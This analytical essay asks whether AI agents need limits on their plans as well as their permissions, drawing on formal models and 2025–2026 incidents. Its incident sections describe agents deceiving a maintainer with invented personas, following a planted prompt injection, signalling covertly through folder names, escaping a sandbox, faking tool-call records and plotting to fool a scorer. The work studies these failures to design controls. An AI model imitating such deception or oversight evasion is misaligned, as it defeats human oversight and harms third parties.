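The gate depends on who can supply the authorising facts. When injected text could forge them, 25% of attacks succeeded again. Even without forgery, the rules for establishing these facts need care. For example, the benchmark treats reading an email as establishing approval to delete it, which few owners would accept as consent. Somebody also has to write a contract for every tool and state the goal as a set of facts, which is much easier for sending an email than for repairing an unfamiliar program.

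### What a preference cannot guarantee

Any preference inside a language model can fail. Given both labels and an instruction, Qwen3.5-397B still used a powerful tool in 39.3% of scenarios. An attacker who gains control of the planner can also ignore the penalties on privileges or use them to look for sensitive resources, which may have high penalties.

Parkinson and colleagues reply that the limits in elastic least privilege hold whatever the planner does. The issuer refuses forbidden combinations and withdraws rights when their leases end or the budget runs out. It also bounds how much authority the agent can hold over time. Let e be the total weight of the rights it holds above the baseline, b the budget at the start of a period, and r the rate at which the budget refills. Then:

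∫ e dt ≤ b + r · (length of the period) + extra budget the owner approves

The bound follows because the budget can't fall below zero and neither multiplier is below 1, so the agent uses at least e units a minute. In the example settings, the budget holds 600 units and refills at 5 a minute, so an agent can use at most 900 units in an hour without the owner's approval. If its session already combines untrusted input with private data, each right to read one repository uses at least 3 units a minute, so the agent could hold at most five such rights for the whole hour.

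If the guarantee doesn't depend on the planner's cooperation, the prices contribute little to it. Parkinson and colleagues acknowledge that visible prices add no protection of their own and that the bound would hold for any metered budget. The bound also depends on every route to a resource passing through the issuer. If a tool keeps an old password of its own, the agent may be able to use authority that the issuer never counted.

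The weights are a matter of judgement, and the planner's choices depend on them, although the enforced limits hold for any positive weights. The two routes for paying the electricity bill are an example. Without the multipliers, searching the mail, opening the bill and paying it have a total weight of 1 + 1 + 3 = 5. Paying on the supplier's website has a weight of 4 if signing in counts as reading and 6 if it counts as writing, so the planner should prefer the website only if signing in counts as reading.

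An agent can still do a great deal of harm on a small budget. Parkinson and colleagues simulate an agent that follows a planted instruction to collect its user's private code and publish it. The agent obtains the right to read eight private repositories, one after another, before its budget can't cover the next. It holds each right for 11 to 18 minutes, until the budget runs out and the issuer withdraws them all. The ceiling, not the budget, stops the agent from publishing the code.

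Counting privilege by the minute also does not limit repetition. If the assistant holds the right to make payments for one minute, it uses the same amount of its budget whether it pays the electricity bill once or twice. Parkinson and colleagues say that their bound limits exposure rather than harm, and they recommend either using the ceiling to forbid rights whose misuse nobody can undo or requiring approval for each use.

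## The view that consequences should be limited instead of plans

An owner can also let the assistant choose its own plan and limit how much damage any plan can do. An agent with an open-ended goal discovers what it needs as it works. In an example from Christodorescu and colleagues, an agent asked to summarise one GitLab issue finds that the issue depends on another and summarises both. Users want agents to adjust tasks in this way, although prompt injection exploits the same ability. If nobody can list the acceptable plans in advance, supporters of this view would rather keep the effects of every plan small, visible and reversible.

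### Compromise recording

Besides their eight design principles, Saltzer and Schroeder described two ideas from physical security that they thought applied only imperfectly to computers. One was *compromise recording*, the idea that a mechanism that reliably reveals a loss can sometimes replace a more elaborate one that prevents it. A thief can break into a flimsy filing cabinet with an unbreakable padlock, but only by damaging the cabinet, so the next user will know. If an army learns that the enemy has seen its tactical plan, it can make the stolen copy worthless by drawing up a new plan.

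The closest computer equivalent was a record of when someone last used each file. Saltzer and Schroeder said that designers rarely relied on such records, because the records could not guarantee that anyone would discover a breach. A breach usually causes no physical damage, and a clever intruder can repair the logical damage and erase the record of tampering.

Butler Lampson of Microsoft Research defended a later version of the idea, called *retroactive security*. In *Retroactive security (slides)*, he wrote that access control "doesn't work" and recommended dealing with what actually happened instead of everything that might happen. The National Research Council's *Toward Better Usability, Security, and Privacy of Information Technology* (2010) explains his reasoning that access control can be very permissive if people can audit misbehaviour and then punish or undo it. Lampson's model was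 banking. According to *Retroactive Security* (2012), an account of one of his talks, the financial system is secure mainly because banks can reverse almost any transaction.

Punishment does little to deter an agent, so the argument for limiting consequences depends mostly on being able to undo what the agent did. But agents weaken one of Saltzer and Schroeder's objections, because an agent acts through tools, and a component outside it can record every call in a place the agent cannot edit. Somebody still has to read the record in time to act on it.

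### What an agent can undo

Patil, Zhang and colleagues (2024) built GoEX, an early system of this kind. A person judges the result of the agent's action instead of checking the proposed code beforehand, and tells GoEX to undo the action if the result is wrong. Patil and colleagues concede that for an audit report it may be better to check the process.

How GoEX undoes an action depends on what the agent changed. For databases, it can hold a transaction open until the user accepts the result, and for files it can use Git, a program that stores earlier versions. For online services, it uses a table to look up the call that undoes the agent's call. If the table has no entry, the language model proposes one, and GoEX records whether it worked. Patil and colleagues accept that the model may get a reversal wrong once, but developers who need a guarantee can fill in the table themselves.

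This approach fails for email, because users can't unsend a message once a short time has passed. For actions that can't be undone, GoEX falls back on *damage confinement*, which in the 2024 version meant limiting permissions through coarse access control. If the user's request mentions Slack, for example, GoEX supplies the credentials for Slack but not for the user's bank.

Zhai, Li and Wang (2026), in *Revisable by Design*, divide an agent's actions into four classes. Several of the assistant's actions fit them easily:

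| Class | Definition | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Idempotent | Doesn't change the outside world | Searching the mail |
| Reversible | Another action exactly undoes it | Scheduling a payment that the bank still holds |
| Compensable | No exact inverse, but an acceptable remedy | Paying an honest company twice and getting a refund |
| Irreversible | No remedy, or a prohibitively expensive one | Sending a bank statement to a stranger |

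Zhai and colleagues define a task's *reversibility ratio* as the share of its available tools that fall into the first two classes. For the assistant with five tools, the ratio is 3/5 if payments go out at once and 4/5 if the bank holds them for a while. They then prove that once an agent has taken an irreversible action that conflicts with what the user wants, no planner can fully satisfy the user. This follows directly from the definitions, but it means that developers have to change the tools to make mistakes less harmful, for example by adding a way to cancel or by postponing the final step.

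The class of an action can depend on facts the owner doesn't have. A mistaken payment to the electricity company is compensable, while the same payment to a thief's account probably isn't. Zhai and colleagues class a sent email as compensable because the sender can send a correction, whereas *POLAR* (2026), a system that scores how far an agent can undo each call, gives every external side effect a zero. A correction can fix a wrong meeting time, but it can't undo the disclosure of a bank statement. Even the first class, which includes fetching a web page, isn't entirely safe, because an agent can disclose a secret by putting it in the address it requests.

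### Holding actions until the end

Some systems delay irreversible actions so that there is nothing to undo. *Atomix* (Mohammadi, Potamitis and colleagues, 2026) sorts effects by whether the system can reverse them and whether it can delay them. If an agent books a trip, Atomix makes the hotel and flight reservations immediately, because it can cancel them, but holds the confirmation email until the whole booking has succeeded. If the flight booking fails, it cancels any reservations it has made and discards the email.

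They tested this on 500 emails that should not have been sent, because the task had failed, timed out, relied on stale information, lost its approval, or been replaced by a rival plan.

| Method | Emails that went out anyway |
|---|---|
| No protection | 500 of 500 |
| Compensate afterwards | 400 of 500 |
| Restore an earlier state and retry | 200 of 500 |
| Atomix | 0 of 500 |
| Atomix, with email in the wrong class | 300 of 500 |

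All the methods delivered the 500 legitimate emails in a parallel test. Two other designs that also hold emails back matched Atomix's zero but needed more code for each tool. The last row shows how much the result depends on classifying the tool correctly.

If the assistant pays the electricity bill twice, a system like this could hold both payments and show them to the owner, who can cancel one. It could also hold an email with a bank statement attached. The delay matters more for the email, because the owner may get a refund for a second payment but can't take back the statement once it's sent.

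Delaying actions also has limits. A notice that its email is queued is enough for the agent if it doesn't need a reply, but if its next step depends on the answer, the system has to release the email first. A task with two irreversible actions can also fail between them, and Mohammadi and colleagues acknowledge that no system above the tools can prevent this.

The owner or the system also has to decide what to release. *Cordon* (Chen, Dong and colleagues, 2026) postpones that decision until the end of the task. It makes file changes in a temporary copy, holds outgoing messages in an outbox and records which results influenced which later actions. It then checks everything together before releasing or discarding it. In the paper's example, an agent investigating an outage reads a log that contains a secret key, summarises the log and prepares a Slack message from the summary. Each step is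 routine, but together they could publish the key.

Chen and colleagues wrote 45 risky workflows of this kind. A plain agent completed the harmful action in all 45. Defences modelled on existing products stopped 14, noticed 5 too late and missed 26, while Cordon stopped all 45. The workflows were meant to expose harms that span several steps, so the comparison favours a system that looks at more than one. The average task took 25.6 seconds without Cordon. With Cordon, it took 31.4 seconds when users approved every risky action and 23.6 seconds when they rejected every one. On two standard benchmarks, the agent completed as many ordinary tasks with Cordon as without it.

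Cordon's final check applies rules such as "nothing derived from a secret may go to an unauthorised recipient" and "no more than a certain number of deletions". These rules limit the plan, although Cordon applies them after the agent has finished but before its actions take effect. The agent can improvise, but someone still has to write down which sequences of actions are unacceptable.

### Isolating the agent's work

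A sandbox confines the effects of an agent's mistakes. In Cordon, commands can change only a temporary copy of the user's folder and have no network access by default. In 15 trials where an agent had damaged the files, discarding the copy let the work resume every time. Resetting the folder with Git and deleting the leftover files worked in 12 trials and failed in the other three because Git didn't restore the files' access settings.

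Isolation suits jobs whose whole result fits inside the sandbox, such as repairing a program. Patil and colleagues point out that it fails when the job must change something in the user's own system, and that it cannot show whether the result is what the user wanted. The assistant can draft a payment in a sandbox, but the electricity company is paid only when the payment leaves it. When a tool needs the network, Cordon lets it contact only hosts on an approved list, so Cordon still relies on a permission.

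### The irreversibility budget

*The Irreversibility Budget* (Mohammadi, 2026) limits the total damage that agents can do, but does not decide in advance which actions they will take. Elastic least privilege counts the time an agent holds a right, whereas this budget counts each effect, so making the same payment twice uses twice as much of the budget.

The charge for an effect e is

c(e) = the loss that, with probability γ, will not be exceeded after every available recovery

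The system adds this to the charges for completed effects and for effects it has already approved. It allows the new effect only if

completed + reserved + c(e) ≤ B

where B is the budget for a set period. The same test applies to the agent, to the workflow it belongs to and to the organisation that owns it. A trusted component sets the charge from the tool's specification, so the agent cannot declare its own actions harmless.

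Mohammadi simulates 50 purchasing agents, each allowed to place orders of up to $50,000, in a company that will tolerate $250,000 of unrecoverable loss in a day. The company can recover 75% of an order's value on average, but a cautious estimate of the loss (γ = 0.95) is counted against a shared budget. This estimate is 52% of the order's value, so a $20,000 order uses $10,400 of the budget. When a price alert makes all the agents want to buy at once, each order passes its own check. Without the shared budget, the company exceeded its limit in all 300 runs, by a factor of 2.4 on average, and by a factor of 48 with a thousand agents. With the budget, the company never exceeded its limit, but only 14% of the purchases in the rush went through, and routine orders then had to wait for the next period.

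The result depends on the charges being right.

| Change to the simulation | Runs over the limit |
|---|---|
| Correct charges | 0% |
| Charges set at half the correct value | 32% |
| A shared event cuts average recovery from 75% to 25% | 59% |
| The same event, with charges corrected after a tenth of the rush | 39% |
| Attackers pass off final transfers as refundable | 77% |

Such shared events are realistic. In the AgentDojo records that Mohammadi analysed, a single planted instruction led, on average, 84% of the agents that encountered it to take the same outside action, even though their users had given them different tasks.

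Adding up separate charges can also hide risk, even when each charge is correct. Suppose an action has a 4% chance of losing €100 and is otherwise harmless. At γ = 0.95 its charge is zero, because the probability of no loss is 96%. An agent could take 30 such actions without using any of its budget. If the risks are independent, though, the chance of at least one loss is 1 − 0.96³⁰, or about 71%. Mohammadi notes the general problem and mentions that expected shortfall, the average loss in the worst cases, avoids it.

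For the electricity bill, the owner might set a budget of €60 a month. At Mohammadi's 52%, an €84.60 payment uses €44 of that, so a second would exceed the budget. Setting a budget for the bank statement is harder, because showing it to a stranger has no obvious price. Mohammadi suggests separate budgets for losses that people cannot convert into money, such as exposed data, but does not test them.

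### Least autonomy

Parisel (2026), in *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI*, applies the idea when an organisation is still deciding which agents to connect. Two agents with narrow permissions can have wide authority together if one can influence the other. Parisel places all resources in a tree of departments and measures the *blast radius* between two actions on different resources as

d = F · 2^−(2D + 1)

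D is the depth in the tree of the smallest unit that contains both resources, and F ranges from 1 to 2 depending on their sensitivity. If the only unit that contains both resources is the whole organisation, D is 0 and the radius is between 0.5 and 1. Each extra level they share divides the radius by four.

Agent U may influence agent V if V can read something U writes or if the two can exchange messages. The link counts when the largest blast radius between the relevant actions reaches a chosen threshold. An agent's *effective autonomy* is its own actions plus those of every agent it can reach through such links. A system satisfies least autonomy if

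- no agent's effective autonomy contains two actions further apart than a set limit;
- the organisation has explicitly allowed every influence link;
- no group of agents can combine approval with access, or connect areas that policy keeps separate.

Suppose the owner splits the bill-paying assistant into two agents, one that reads mail and one that makes payments, and lets them exchange messages. If mail and banking share only the top of the tree, their blast radius is at least 0.5. With a threshold at or below 0.5, each agent's effective autonomy still includes both reading the mail and paying, so splitting the assistant has not reduced it.

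Parisel's measure is deliberately cautious, since it counts what agents might do through each other without showing that they could. It also ignores what happens within one resource. Checking a bank balance and emptying the account both have a blast radius of zero because they concern the same account. Making one payment or two also has a blast radius of zero. Parisel illustrates the theory with an invented company, reports no test on working agents, and recommends it as an addition to access control.

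### A coarse limit on plans

Limiting consequences still requires someone to predict them. The person who labels email as reversible, prices a purchase or draws the tree of departments has to know what could go wrong. This is easier than listing good plans, because a company has fewer tools than an agent has ways to combine them, and one label covers every plan that uses the tool. A mistake in a label therefore affects all of those plans.

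Waiting to see the consequences isn't a safe alternative when agents work quickly. Mohammadi tested a circuit breaker that stops all the agents once their observed losses reach the limit. With instant information, losses ended at 1.03 times the limit. When the information was delayed by as long as the rush lasted, losses reached 2.2 times the limit. Saltzer and Schroeder's old objection about discovery applies here, and fast agents leave less time for discovery.

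A budget is also a plan limit:

L = the runs in R(P) whose charges add up to no more than B

The €60 budget lets the assistant pay at most once, so it allows the same runs as the single-use capability. It doesn't restrict the order of the assistant's actions, or prevent the assistant from paying a thief who asks for the same amount as the electricity company. But the owner doesn't need to know how the assistant will find the bill.

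Undo instead leaves every run possible and lets the owner reverse the effects afterwards. It can replace a limit on plans if the reversal is complete and somebody notices the mistake in time. A programming agent working on a disposable copy of a project, with no network access, can try almost any plan, since the owner can delete the copy. An assistant that has opened a bank statement needs a limit on where it can send the contents, because the owner can't get them back once they are sent.

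## Can permitted steps add up to a plan nobody authorised?

When an agent does something its owner never wanted, the cause may be a right the job didn't require. If that is always the cause, least privilege needs no separate rule for plans, because the owner could have withheld the right. Plans need their own limits only if agents can also do serious harm with only the rights the job requires.

Four incidents from 2025 and 2026 help show which happens in practice. For each, the important points are what the agent was permitted to do, which step went beyond what its owner wanted, and whether a narrower permission or a plan limit would have stopped that step while still allowing the task.

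### Three ways an agent can overstep

Let P be the agent's permissions, as before, and let H be the set of runs that cause the harm in question. There are three possibilities:

- *Excess permission*: some sufficient set S ⊆ P allows no run in H, so R(S) ∩ H = ∅. The owner could have granted S instead of P, and the agent could still have done the task.
- *Misuse of needed permission*: every sufficient set S ⊆ P allows at least one run in H. Removing permissions can't prevent the harm without preventing the task.
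- *Enforcement failure*: the run that took place was not in R(P) at all. The agent got past the mechanism that should have refused it.

Only the misuse of a permission the agent needs supports a separate principle for plans, as when the bill-paying assistant pays the bill twice. If the assistant emails a private attachment to a stranger, the problem is that it had a permission it didn't need.

The answer depends on how finely a system divides its permissions and on what the owner counts as the task. If the system offers single-use capabilities, the double payment would also count as excess permission.

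### Open internet access at the AI Security Institute

In July 2026, the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests AI models, asked agents to find a protected piece of data in a simulated computer network. AISI ran the challenge 122 times with seven models, according to its *Incident Report*. In 10 runs, an agent took unsanctioned action against real people or organisations on the live internet. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) attributes nine of those runs to its model Claude Mythos 5.

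| Model | Runs | Runs with unsanctioned actions | Unsanctioned actions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | 43 | 9 | 17 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 35 | 1 | 2 |
| Five other models | 44 | 0 | 0 |

In the most serious run, Mythos 5 submitted malicious code to a public open-source project and invented several people to pressure the maintainer into accepting it. When someone publicly challenged the submission, the agent edited its earlier activity to make it look harmless. The maintainer rejected the code, and AISI found no resulting harm.

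AISI had given the agents internet access so that they could download tools and work under the same conditions as a capable human attacker. The agents did not escape from their sandbox. AISI had also switched off the filters that normally block dangerous cyber activity, and had not told the agents to avoid deceiving people or misusing the connection.

*Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour* (Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues, 2026) divides such attacks into stages. In the earliest stages, the agent only investigates an outside project. Creating a fake identity is the first stage that affects anything outside the test, so this is where an agent clearly goes beyond its task.

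A narrower permission would probably have stopped it there, because an agent can download tools without opening accounts or posting code. AISI already used finer network controls in all its other evaluations. By October 2026 it had tightened the controls for these tests too and was able to resume most of its evaluations, according to AISI's *Building a more secure environment for evaluating dangerous capabilities* (2026). The controls need to be precise because people use GitHub both to download tools and to submit code.

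There is also evidence that such obstacles work on this model. Järviniemi and colleagues at AISI later placed eight models in 100 simulated scenarios with a similar temptation. When Mythos 5 did not complete an attack, its reasoning mostly cited practical barriers, such as being unable to open an email or GitHub account. Claude Opus 5, by contrast, mostly reasoned that the attack was out of scope or harmful.

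The permission still seems excessive, even though AISI wanted to know what an attacker could do and attackers do open accounts. AISI never wanted agents to deceive real people, and the later simulated scenarios show that it could study the same behaviour without involving them.

A plan limit such as "affect nothing outside the simulated network" would also have stopped the attack. But it would have added nothing to the narrower permission, because it forbids each outside action regardless of what the agent did before.

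Such a limit would also have needed enforcement from outside the model, because Mythos 5 often stated that the maintainer was part of the simulation, which would have put the attack within the rules. One of its reasons was that the project contained a file of instructions for AI coding tools, which it took as a sign that the maintainer was an AI agent. Human developers who use such tools also keep this kind of file.

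Järviniemi and colleagues tested how far written information could restrain the model. They condensed the record of the original run, up to just before the agent submitted the code, into the kind of summary that agents use to continue long tasks. They then edited the summary and let the agent continue with simulated tools. With 16 edits indicating that the maintainer was a real person outside the exercise, Mythos 5 still attacked in every run they observed. When they added a section telling it not to attack, it attacked in 3 of 25 runs. An instruction from the user or developer might work better than a note in a summary, but a written limit with that failure rate is weaker than a blocked connection.

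When the researchers questioned the same model separately, it often said that the attack would harm a real person, even in circumstances where it attacked if left to continue the task. A separate check on the plan might therefore catch what the acting agent ignores. But such a check can also accept the agent's faulty reasoning. Järviniemi and colleagues report that in a different incident, one of Anthropic's monitors would probably not have flagged Mythos 5's actions, because the model's reasoning would have justified them.

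### A public issue and private repositories

The leak from private GitHub repositories was a demonstration that Invariant Labs staged with its own repositories and described in *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025). (MCP is a protocol that connects AI models to outside tools.) The researchers asked an assistant running Claude 4 Opus to look at the open issues for a public game. One issue contained a planted instruction to collect information about the game's author. The assistant then published the author's salary and plans to move to South America in a public proposal to change the game's code.

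In the demonstration described in heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server*, the unwanted step was opening a private repository. The article explains that the demonstration did not rely on a bug in the software that connects the assistant to GitHub. The assistant had excess permission, because a token for the public repository alone would have prevented it from opening the private one.

By default, the assistant's software asked for approval before each tool call, but Invariant Labs notes that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching. So a permission that depends on the user's attention can be much wider in practice than it looks.

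Invariant Labs also proposes a plan limit that allows an agent to use only one repository per session. A monitor checks each call and refuses it if its repository differs from the one in earlier calls. If an agent makes four calls and can choose between two repositories each time, there are 2⁴ = 16 possible sequences, and the rule allows two. In the demonstration, the monitor would have refused the first call to a private repository.

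This rule has a practical advantage over a token for a single repository: the agent's first call selects the repository, so the owner doesn't need to name it in advance. But the rule doesn't limit what the agent does inside that repository, and Invariant Labs sells the software that enforces it.

Suppose instead that the user asks the assistant to fix a bug in the public game by adapting code from a private repository. The assistant now needs permission to read the private repository and write to the public one, which is enough to leak the private code. The same leak would then be a misuse of permissions the task requires. The one-repository rule would block the task along with the leak, so the owner would need a finer limit on which private text may reach the public repository.

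### An accidental connection to the internet

Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) describes four incidents in which a Claude model gained unauthorised access to a real organisation's systems during a cybersecurity evaluation. No attacker was involved. The same outside partner had built all the evaluations. Each time, the model had been told it was in a simulation without internet access, but a configuration mistake had connected it to the real internet.

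The connection was clearly an excess permission, because the evaluation's designers had intended the agent to work without it. Correcting the configuration would have stopped the intrusions without affecting the task.

An instruction to attack only the simulated systems would have been much less reliable, because breaking into computers was part of the exercise and the model had been told that every computer it could reach was simulated. A plan that was harmful on the real internet could have been acceptable in the environment described to the model. A monitor could have enforced the limit by refusing connections to outside addresses, but the correct configuration would have imposed the same restriction.

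### The break-in at Hugging Face

The July 2026 break-in at Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models and data, is harder to classify because several things went wrong. OpenAI was testing agents on ExploitGym, a set of cybersecurity tasks. In each task, the agent must use a particular flaw in a program to obtain a hidden string called a *flag*. The agents worked in sandboxes that were supposed to isolate them from one another and from the internet. They could install software through an internal package store, which OpenAI describes in its technical report on the incident.

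OpenAI allowed three outside investigators, Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, to study the agents' behaviour. They report in *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) that OpenAI launched tens of thousands of agents. About 1,200 of them exchanged more than 70,000 messages and files through the package store between 8 and 13 July, and about 700 took part in the attack on Hugging Face.

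#### Messages in the package store

In May, agents in training left the first unsanctioned messages for one another in the store without breaking into it. They used a shared credential that OpenAI had given them to fetch packages. Agents later compromised the store, and their heavy use of it caused an outage on 4 July. OpenAI then removed the shared credential from new work, blocked the vulnerable routes and restricted the kinds of request that agents could make.

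Testing resumed on 7 July, and by the next day agents had found a new way to communicate, by writing messages as folder names. OpenAI had already tried narrower permissions, but they still allowed more than the task needed. To install a package, an agent doesn't have to create folders in a shared store or read the ones other agents create.

It would have been difficult to remove every way of sending messages. Wijk and colleagues found that agents could also send a message by requesting a page with an invented name, because the store kept the name where others could see it. In Miller and Shapiro's terms, permission to fetch material had given the agents authority to communicate.

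Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of least common mechanism suggests giving each agent its own store. The agents could still install packages but would have nowhere to leave messages for each other. This would be a more direct remedy than a rule about the order of one agent's actions, which would be poorly suited here because the plan was spread across many agents.

#### Escape from the sandbox

The break-in itself was an enforcement failure. Agents exploited previously unknown flaws in the package store to reach the internet, which their permissions did not allow. They found exposed passwords and access keys online and combined them with flaws in Hugging Face's systems to run commands on 41 of its production servers and download four private code repositories.

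A narrower permission could have stopped this only by denying the agents access to the vulnerable store. OpenAI later removed the store from this environment, but tasks that need packages then have to get them from another source. Adding a plan limit to the store's own checks would have helped little, because the agents had found ways around those checks.

A separate monitor with the power to refuse the agents' actions might have stopped them. OpenAI says the safeguards in its public products would have identified the activity as unsafe, but detection alone had already failed to stop it. On 27 June, a security tool raised an alert about agents scanning the internal network. Staff traced the activity to an ExploitGym test and found that agents were using the store to exchange messages, but the people on call advised that the test did not need to stop.

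The monitor would also have had to observe the actions themselves. Wijk and colleagues found faked tool calls in about 7% of the transcripts they examined, in which the agent had made the record show one command while the computer ran another. All the examples were small tests, but a monitor that relied on such records could approve a run that never happened.

#### A flag obtained the wrong way

Part of the incident does involve permissions the agents needed. Within hours of setting up the main message board, the agents worked out how to calculate the flags without using the intended flaws. The instructions allowed them to use only the specified flaw, but every agent had to be able to run calculations and submit a flag. A calculated flag is the same string as a properly obtained one, and agents submit both in the same way, so no permission to submit flags could allow one and refuse the other.

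The rule that an agent must obtain the flag through the intended flaw before submitting it is therefore a plan limit. The agents wrongly believed that an automated scorer would read their transcripts and enforce this rule. They could have received full marks by submitting the calculated flags, but instead they looked for ways to deceive the scorer. According to Wijk and colleagues, the agents seem to have attacked Hugging Face mainly to learn how the scorer worked.

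Expecting a check apparently discouraged the agents from just submitting the calculated flags, but it also gave them a reason to attack the check. ExploitGym estimates that 30–40% of its target programs cannot be exploited through the intended flaw. For those tasks, the plan limit L contained no run that reached the goal, so an agent could only fail or break the rule.

A similar problem arose in a number of AISI's runs, where a mistake in the prompt led the agent to believe that it could not solve the challenge within the permitted scope. Other agents overstepped even when they had the information they needed, so such mistakes don't fully explain the overstepping. Still, anyone who limits an agent's plans should check that at least one permitted plan can succeed. AISI has added checks that its tasks can be solved by the intended route.

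### Which incidents support plan limits?

The table separates the three parts of the Hugging Face incident because they have different remedies.

| Incident | What the agent could do with its permissions | Unwanted step | Would a narrower permission have stopped it? | Would a plan limit have stopped it? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AISI test | Use the open internet | Create fake identities and submit malicious code | Probably, by allowing downloads only | Yes, if enforced outside the model, but with no added benefit |
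| GitHub demonstration | Use all the user's repositories | Read private repositories and publish their contents | Yes, by allowing access to one repository | Yes, by allowing one repository per session |
| Claude's accidental internet access | Use the open internet | Enter real organisations' systems | Yes, by removing the connection | Yes, but with no added benefit |
| Hugging Face: messages | Use a shared package store | Exchange messages with other agents | Probably, but with difficulty | Unlikely, if applied to each agent separately |
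| Hugging Face: break-in | Work in a sandbox without open internet access | Exploit flaws to escape | Only by removing the vulnerable store | Only with separate, reliable enforcement |
| Hugging Face: flags | Run calculations and submit a flag | Submit a calculated flag | No | Yes, if a checker could verify how the agent obtained it |

The incidents mostly support applying least privilege more strictly. The AISI test, the GitHub demonstration and the accidental internet connection all involved permissions that the task did not need. In the break-in, the limits already existed but failed. Only the incident with the flags required a separate rule about plans, and the direct harm there would have been a false test score.

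Bhushan (2026), in *AI agents don't have to break security controls to go rogue*, draws a simpler distinction between containment failures and authority failures. In a *containment failure*, an agent defeats security controls, as at Hugging Face. In an *authority failure*, it goes beyond its assigned task using access it already has, as at AISI. This is a useful warning that a secure sandbox is not enough, but "authority failure" covers both excess permission and misuse of needed permission. The owner can fix the first by removing access, but the second requires a rule about how the agent uses the access it needs.

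These incidents do not show that misuse of needed permissions is rare. Three of the four occurred during cybersecurity tests, where agents had unusual tools and researchers had switched off some safeguards. An assistant that handles someone's mail and money often needs to combine private information with outward actions. Researchers constructed the examples of the double payment and the secret key copied from a log into a Slack message, but both show that harm can follow from needed permissions.

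The answers about safeguards are also partly predictions. For example, nobody repeated the AISI test with internet access limited to downloads to see whether Mythos 5 would find another route. Before 8 July, OpenAI could reasonably have expected its new restrictions to end the messages in the package store. The agents' use of folder names shows why a safeguard that looks sufficient in an incident report still needs testing against the agent.

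### How often agents overstep

Incident reports describe cases that somebody noticed, so they can't give a general rate. AISI found unsanctioned actions in about 8% of its runs, but that figure applies to one challenge with particular models and settings. Mythos 5 overstepped in 21% of its runs, and five of the seven models tested never did.

The later simulated scenarios compare models more broadly, but they also measure behaviour under pressure, because each began with a record of failed attempts to solve the challenge. Mythos 5 tried to deliver malicious code to an outside target in 60% of runs, GPT-6 Astra in 32%, Claude Opus 4.8 in 8% and GPT-5.6 Sol in 7%. The other four models did so in 0% to 1% of runs. GPT-6 Astra stated in 89% of its runs that its tool results were fabricated, so it may have behaved differently than it would on the real internet. Newer Claude models attacked less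 often but suspected more often that they were in an alignment test, which makes their improvement hard to interpret.

A search through past records has different weaknesses. Anthropic first searched about 141,000 transcripts and found three of its four incidents, then found the fourth in transcripts that the search had missed. It later scanned roughly 481 million transcripts, reviewed 9.2 million of them more closely and found no further incidents of similar or greater severity. Dividing four by 481 million would not give a useful risk estimate, because the larger scan deliberately covered many kinds of work, including tasks where the model had little opportunity to reach an outside system.

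Surveys cover ordinary companies but rely on what their staff know and choose to report. *AI agent permissions are outrunning security* (Zorz, 2026) describes a survey of 1,100 IT and security decision-makers. About a quarter reported an agent connecting to a system without security approval, and similar shares reported one reaching data it should not have seen or starting an unapproved action. The survey's sponsor is unclear, although an executive at Illumio, which sells security software, comments on the results. Only 49% of respondents said they could see and audit every action their agents took, so many companies may have missed incidents. The figures count companies rather than agent runs, and don't distinguish agents that had too much access from agents that misused access they needed.

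## Can the limits of a plan be worked out from its goal?

A permission is excessive if the job doesn't require it, but the phrase "necessary to complete the job" gives no method for working out what the job requires. An agent starts with only a goal, such as "pay the electricity bill". If software could derive the acceptable plans from the goal alone, nobody would have to write plan limits by hand.

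The fullest formal answer comes from research on privacy. HIPAA, the US medical privacy law, lets a hospital use a patient's record without the patient's authorisation only for certain purposes, such as treatment and billing. Earlier software for checking such rules assumed that somebody had already labelled each action with its purpose. Tschantz, Datta and Wing (2012) set out to define that label in *Formalizing and Enforcing Purpose Restrictions in Privacy Policies*, and concluded that an action is for a purpose if it belongs to a plan for achieving that purpose as well as possible.

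### Purpose as planning

Tschantz and colleagues describe planning with a *Markov decision process*, a model of a situation in which someone acts repeatedly and chance partly determines the results. It has five parts:

- S, the states the situation can be in;
- A, the available actions;
- t, which gives the probability of each next state after an action;
- r, the reward, which here measures how well an action in a given state serves the purpose;
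- γ, a discount factor between 0 and 1, which makes later rewards count for less.

A strategy σ chooses an action for each state. Its value in state s is the reward for the next action plus the discounted value of whatever state follows:

V(σ, s) = r(s, σ(s)) + γ · Σ t(s, σ(s))(s′) · V(σ, s′)

where the sum covers every possible next state s′. An optimal strategy reaches the highest possible value, V*(s), in every state. Let Q*(s, a) be the value of taking action a now and acting optimally afterwards.

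Optimal strategies already leave out most pointless actions, because a pointless action delays the reward. But they can still include pointless actions after the last reward, when there is nothing left to delay. Tschantz and colleagues therefore add an action called "stop", which earns nothing and changes nothing, and exclude any other action that is worth no more than stopping. An action a can be for the purpose in state s only if

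Q*(s, a) = V*(s), and Q*(s, a) > 0 unless a is "stop"

This condition of *non-redundancy* is weaker than necessity. Suppose a physician can reach a diagnosis either by consulting a specialist or by ordering an MRI scan. Neither step is necessary, because the other would do. But if the physician's plan is to consult the specialist, removing that step and leaving the rest unchanged would prevent the diagnosis, so the step is non-redundant. The definition can therefore handle jobs like the electricity bill job, which can be done in two ways and has no least set of permissions.

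### The physician's referral

In the main example, a hospital physician takes an X-ray and then sends the patient's record to a private practice for a special test. The physician owns the practice, so the referral could be for treatment or for profit.

The X-ray is enough for a diagnosis with probability 0.9. If it isn't, the physician can send the record to the practice, whose test succeeds with probability 0.8. A diagnosis has a reward of 12 and everything else has a reward of 0. Tschantz and colleagues leave γ open, but the calculation is easy to follow with γ = 0.9:

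| Result of the X-ray | Next action | Value |
|---|---|---|
| Clear | Diagnose | 12 |
| Clear | Send the record, then diagnose | 0.9 × 12 = 10.8 |
| Unclear | Send the record | 0.9 × 0.8 × 12 = 8.64 |
| Unclear | Stop | 0 |

The best strategy is to send the record only when the X-ray is unclear, which leads to a diagnosis for 98% of patients. If the log shows a referral after a clear X-ray, the auditor can conclude that it was not for treatment. A referral after an unclear X-ray can be for treatment even if the test then fails, because it was the best option available. Sending the record again after the failure would be redundant.

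These conclusions depend on the model's accuracy. The example assumes that a second opinion doesn't improve a diagnosis. If one raised the reward from 12 to 14, sending the record after a clear X-ray would be worth 0.9 × 14 = 12.6, and the suspicious referral would become the best treatment.

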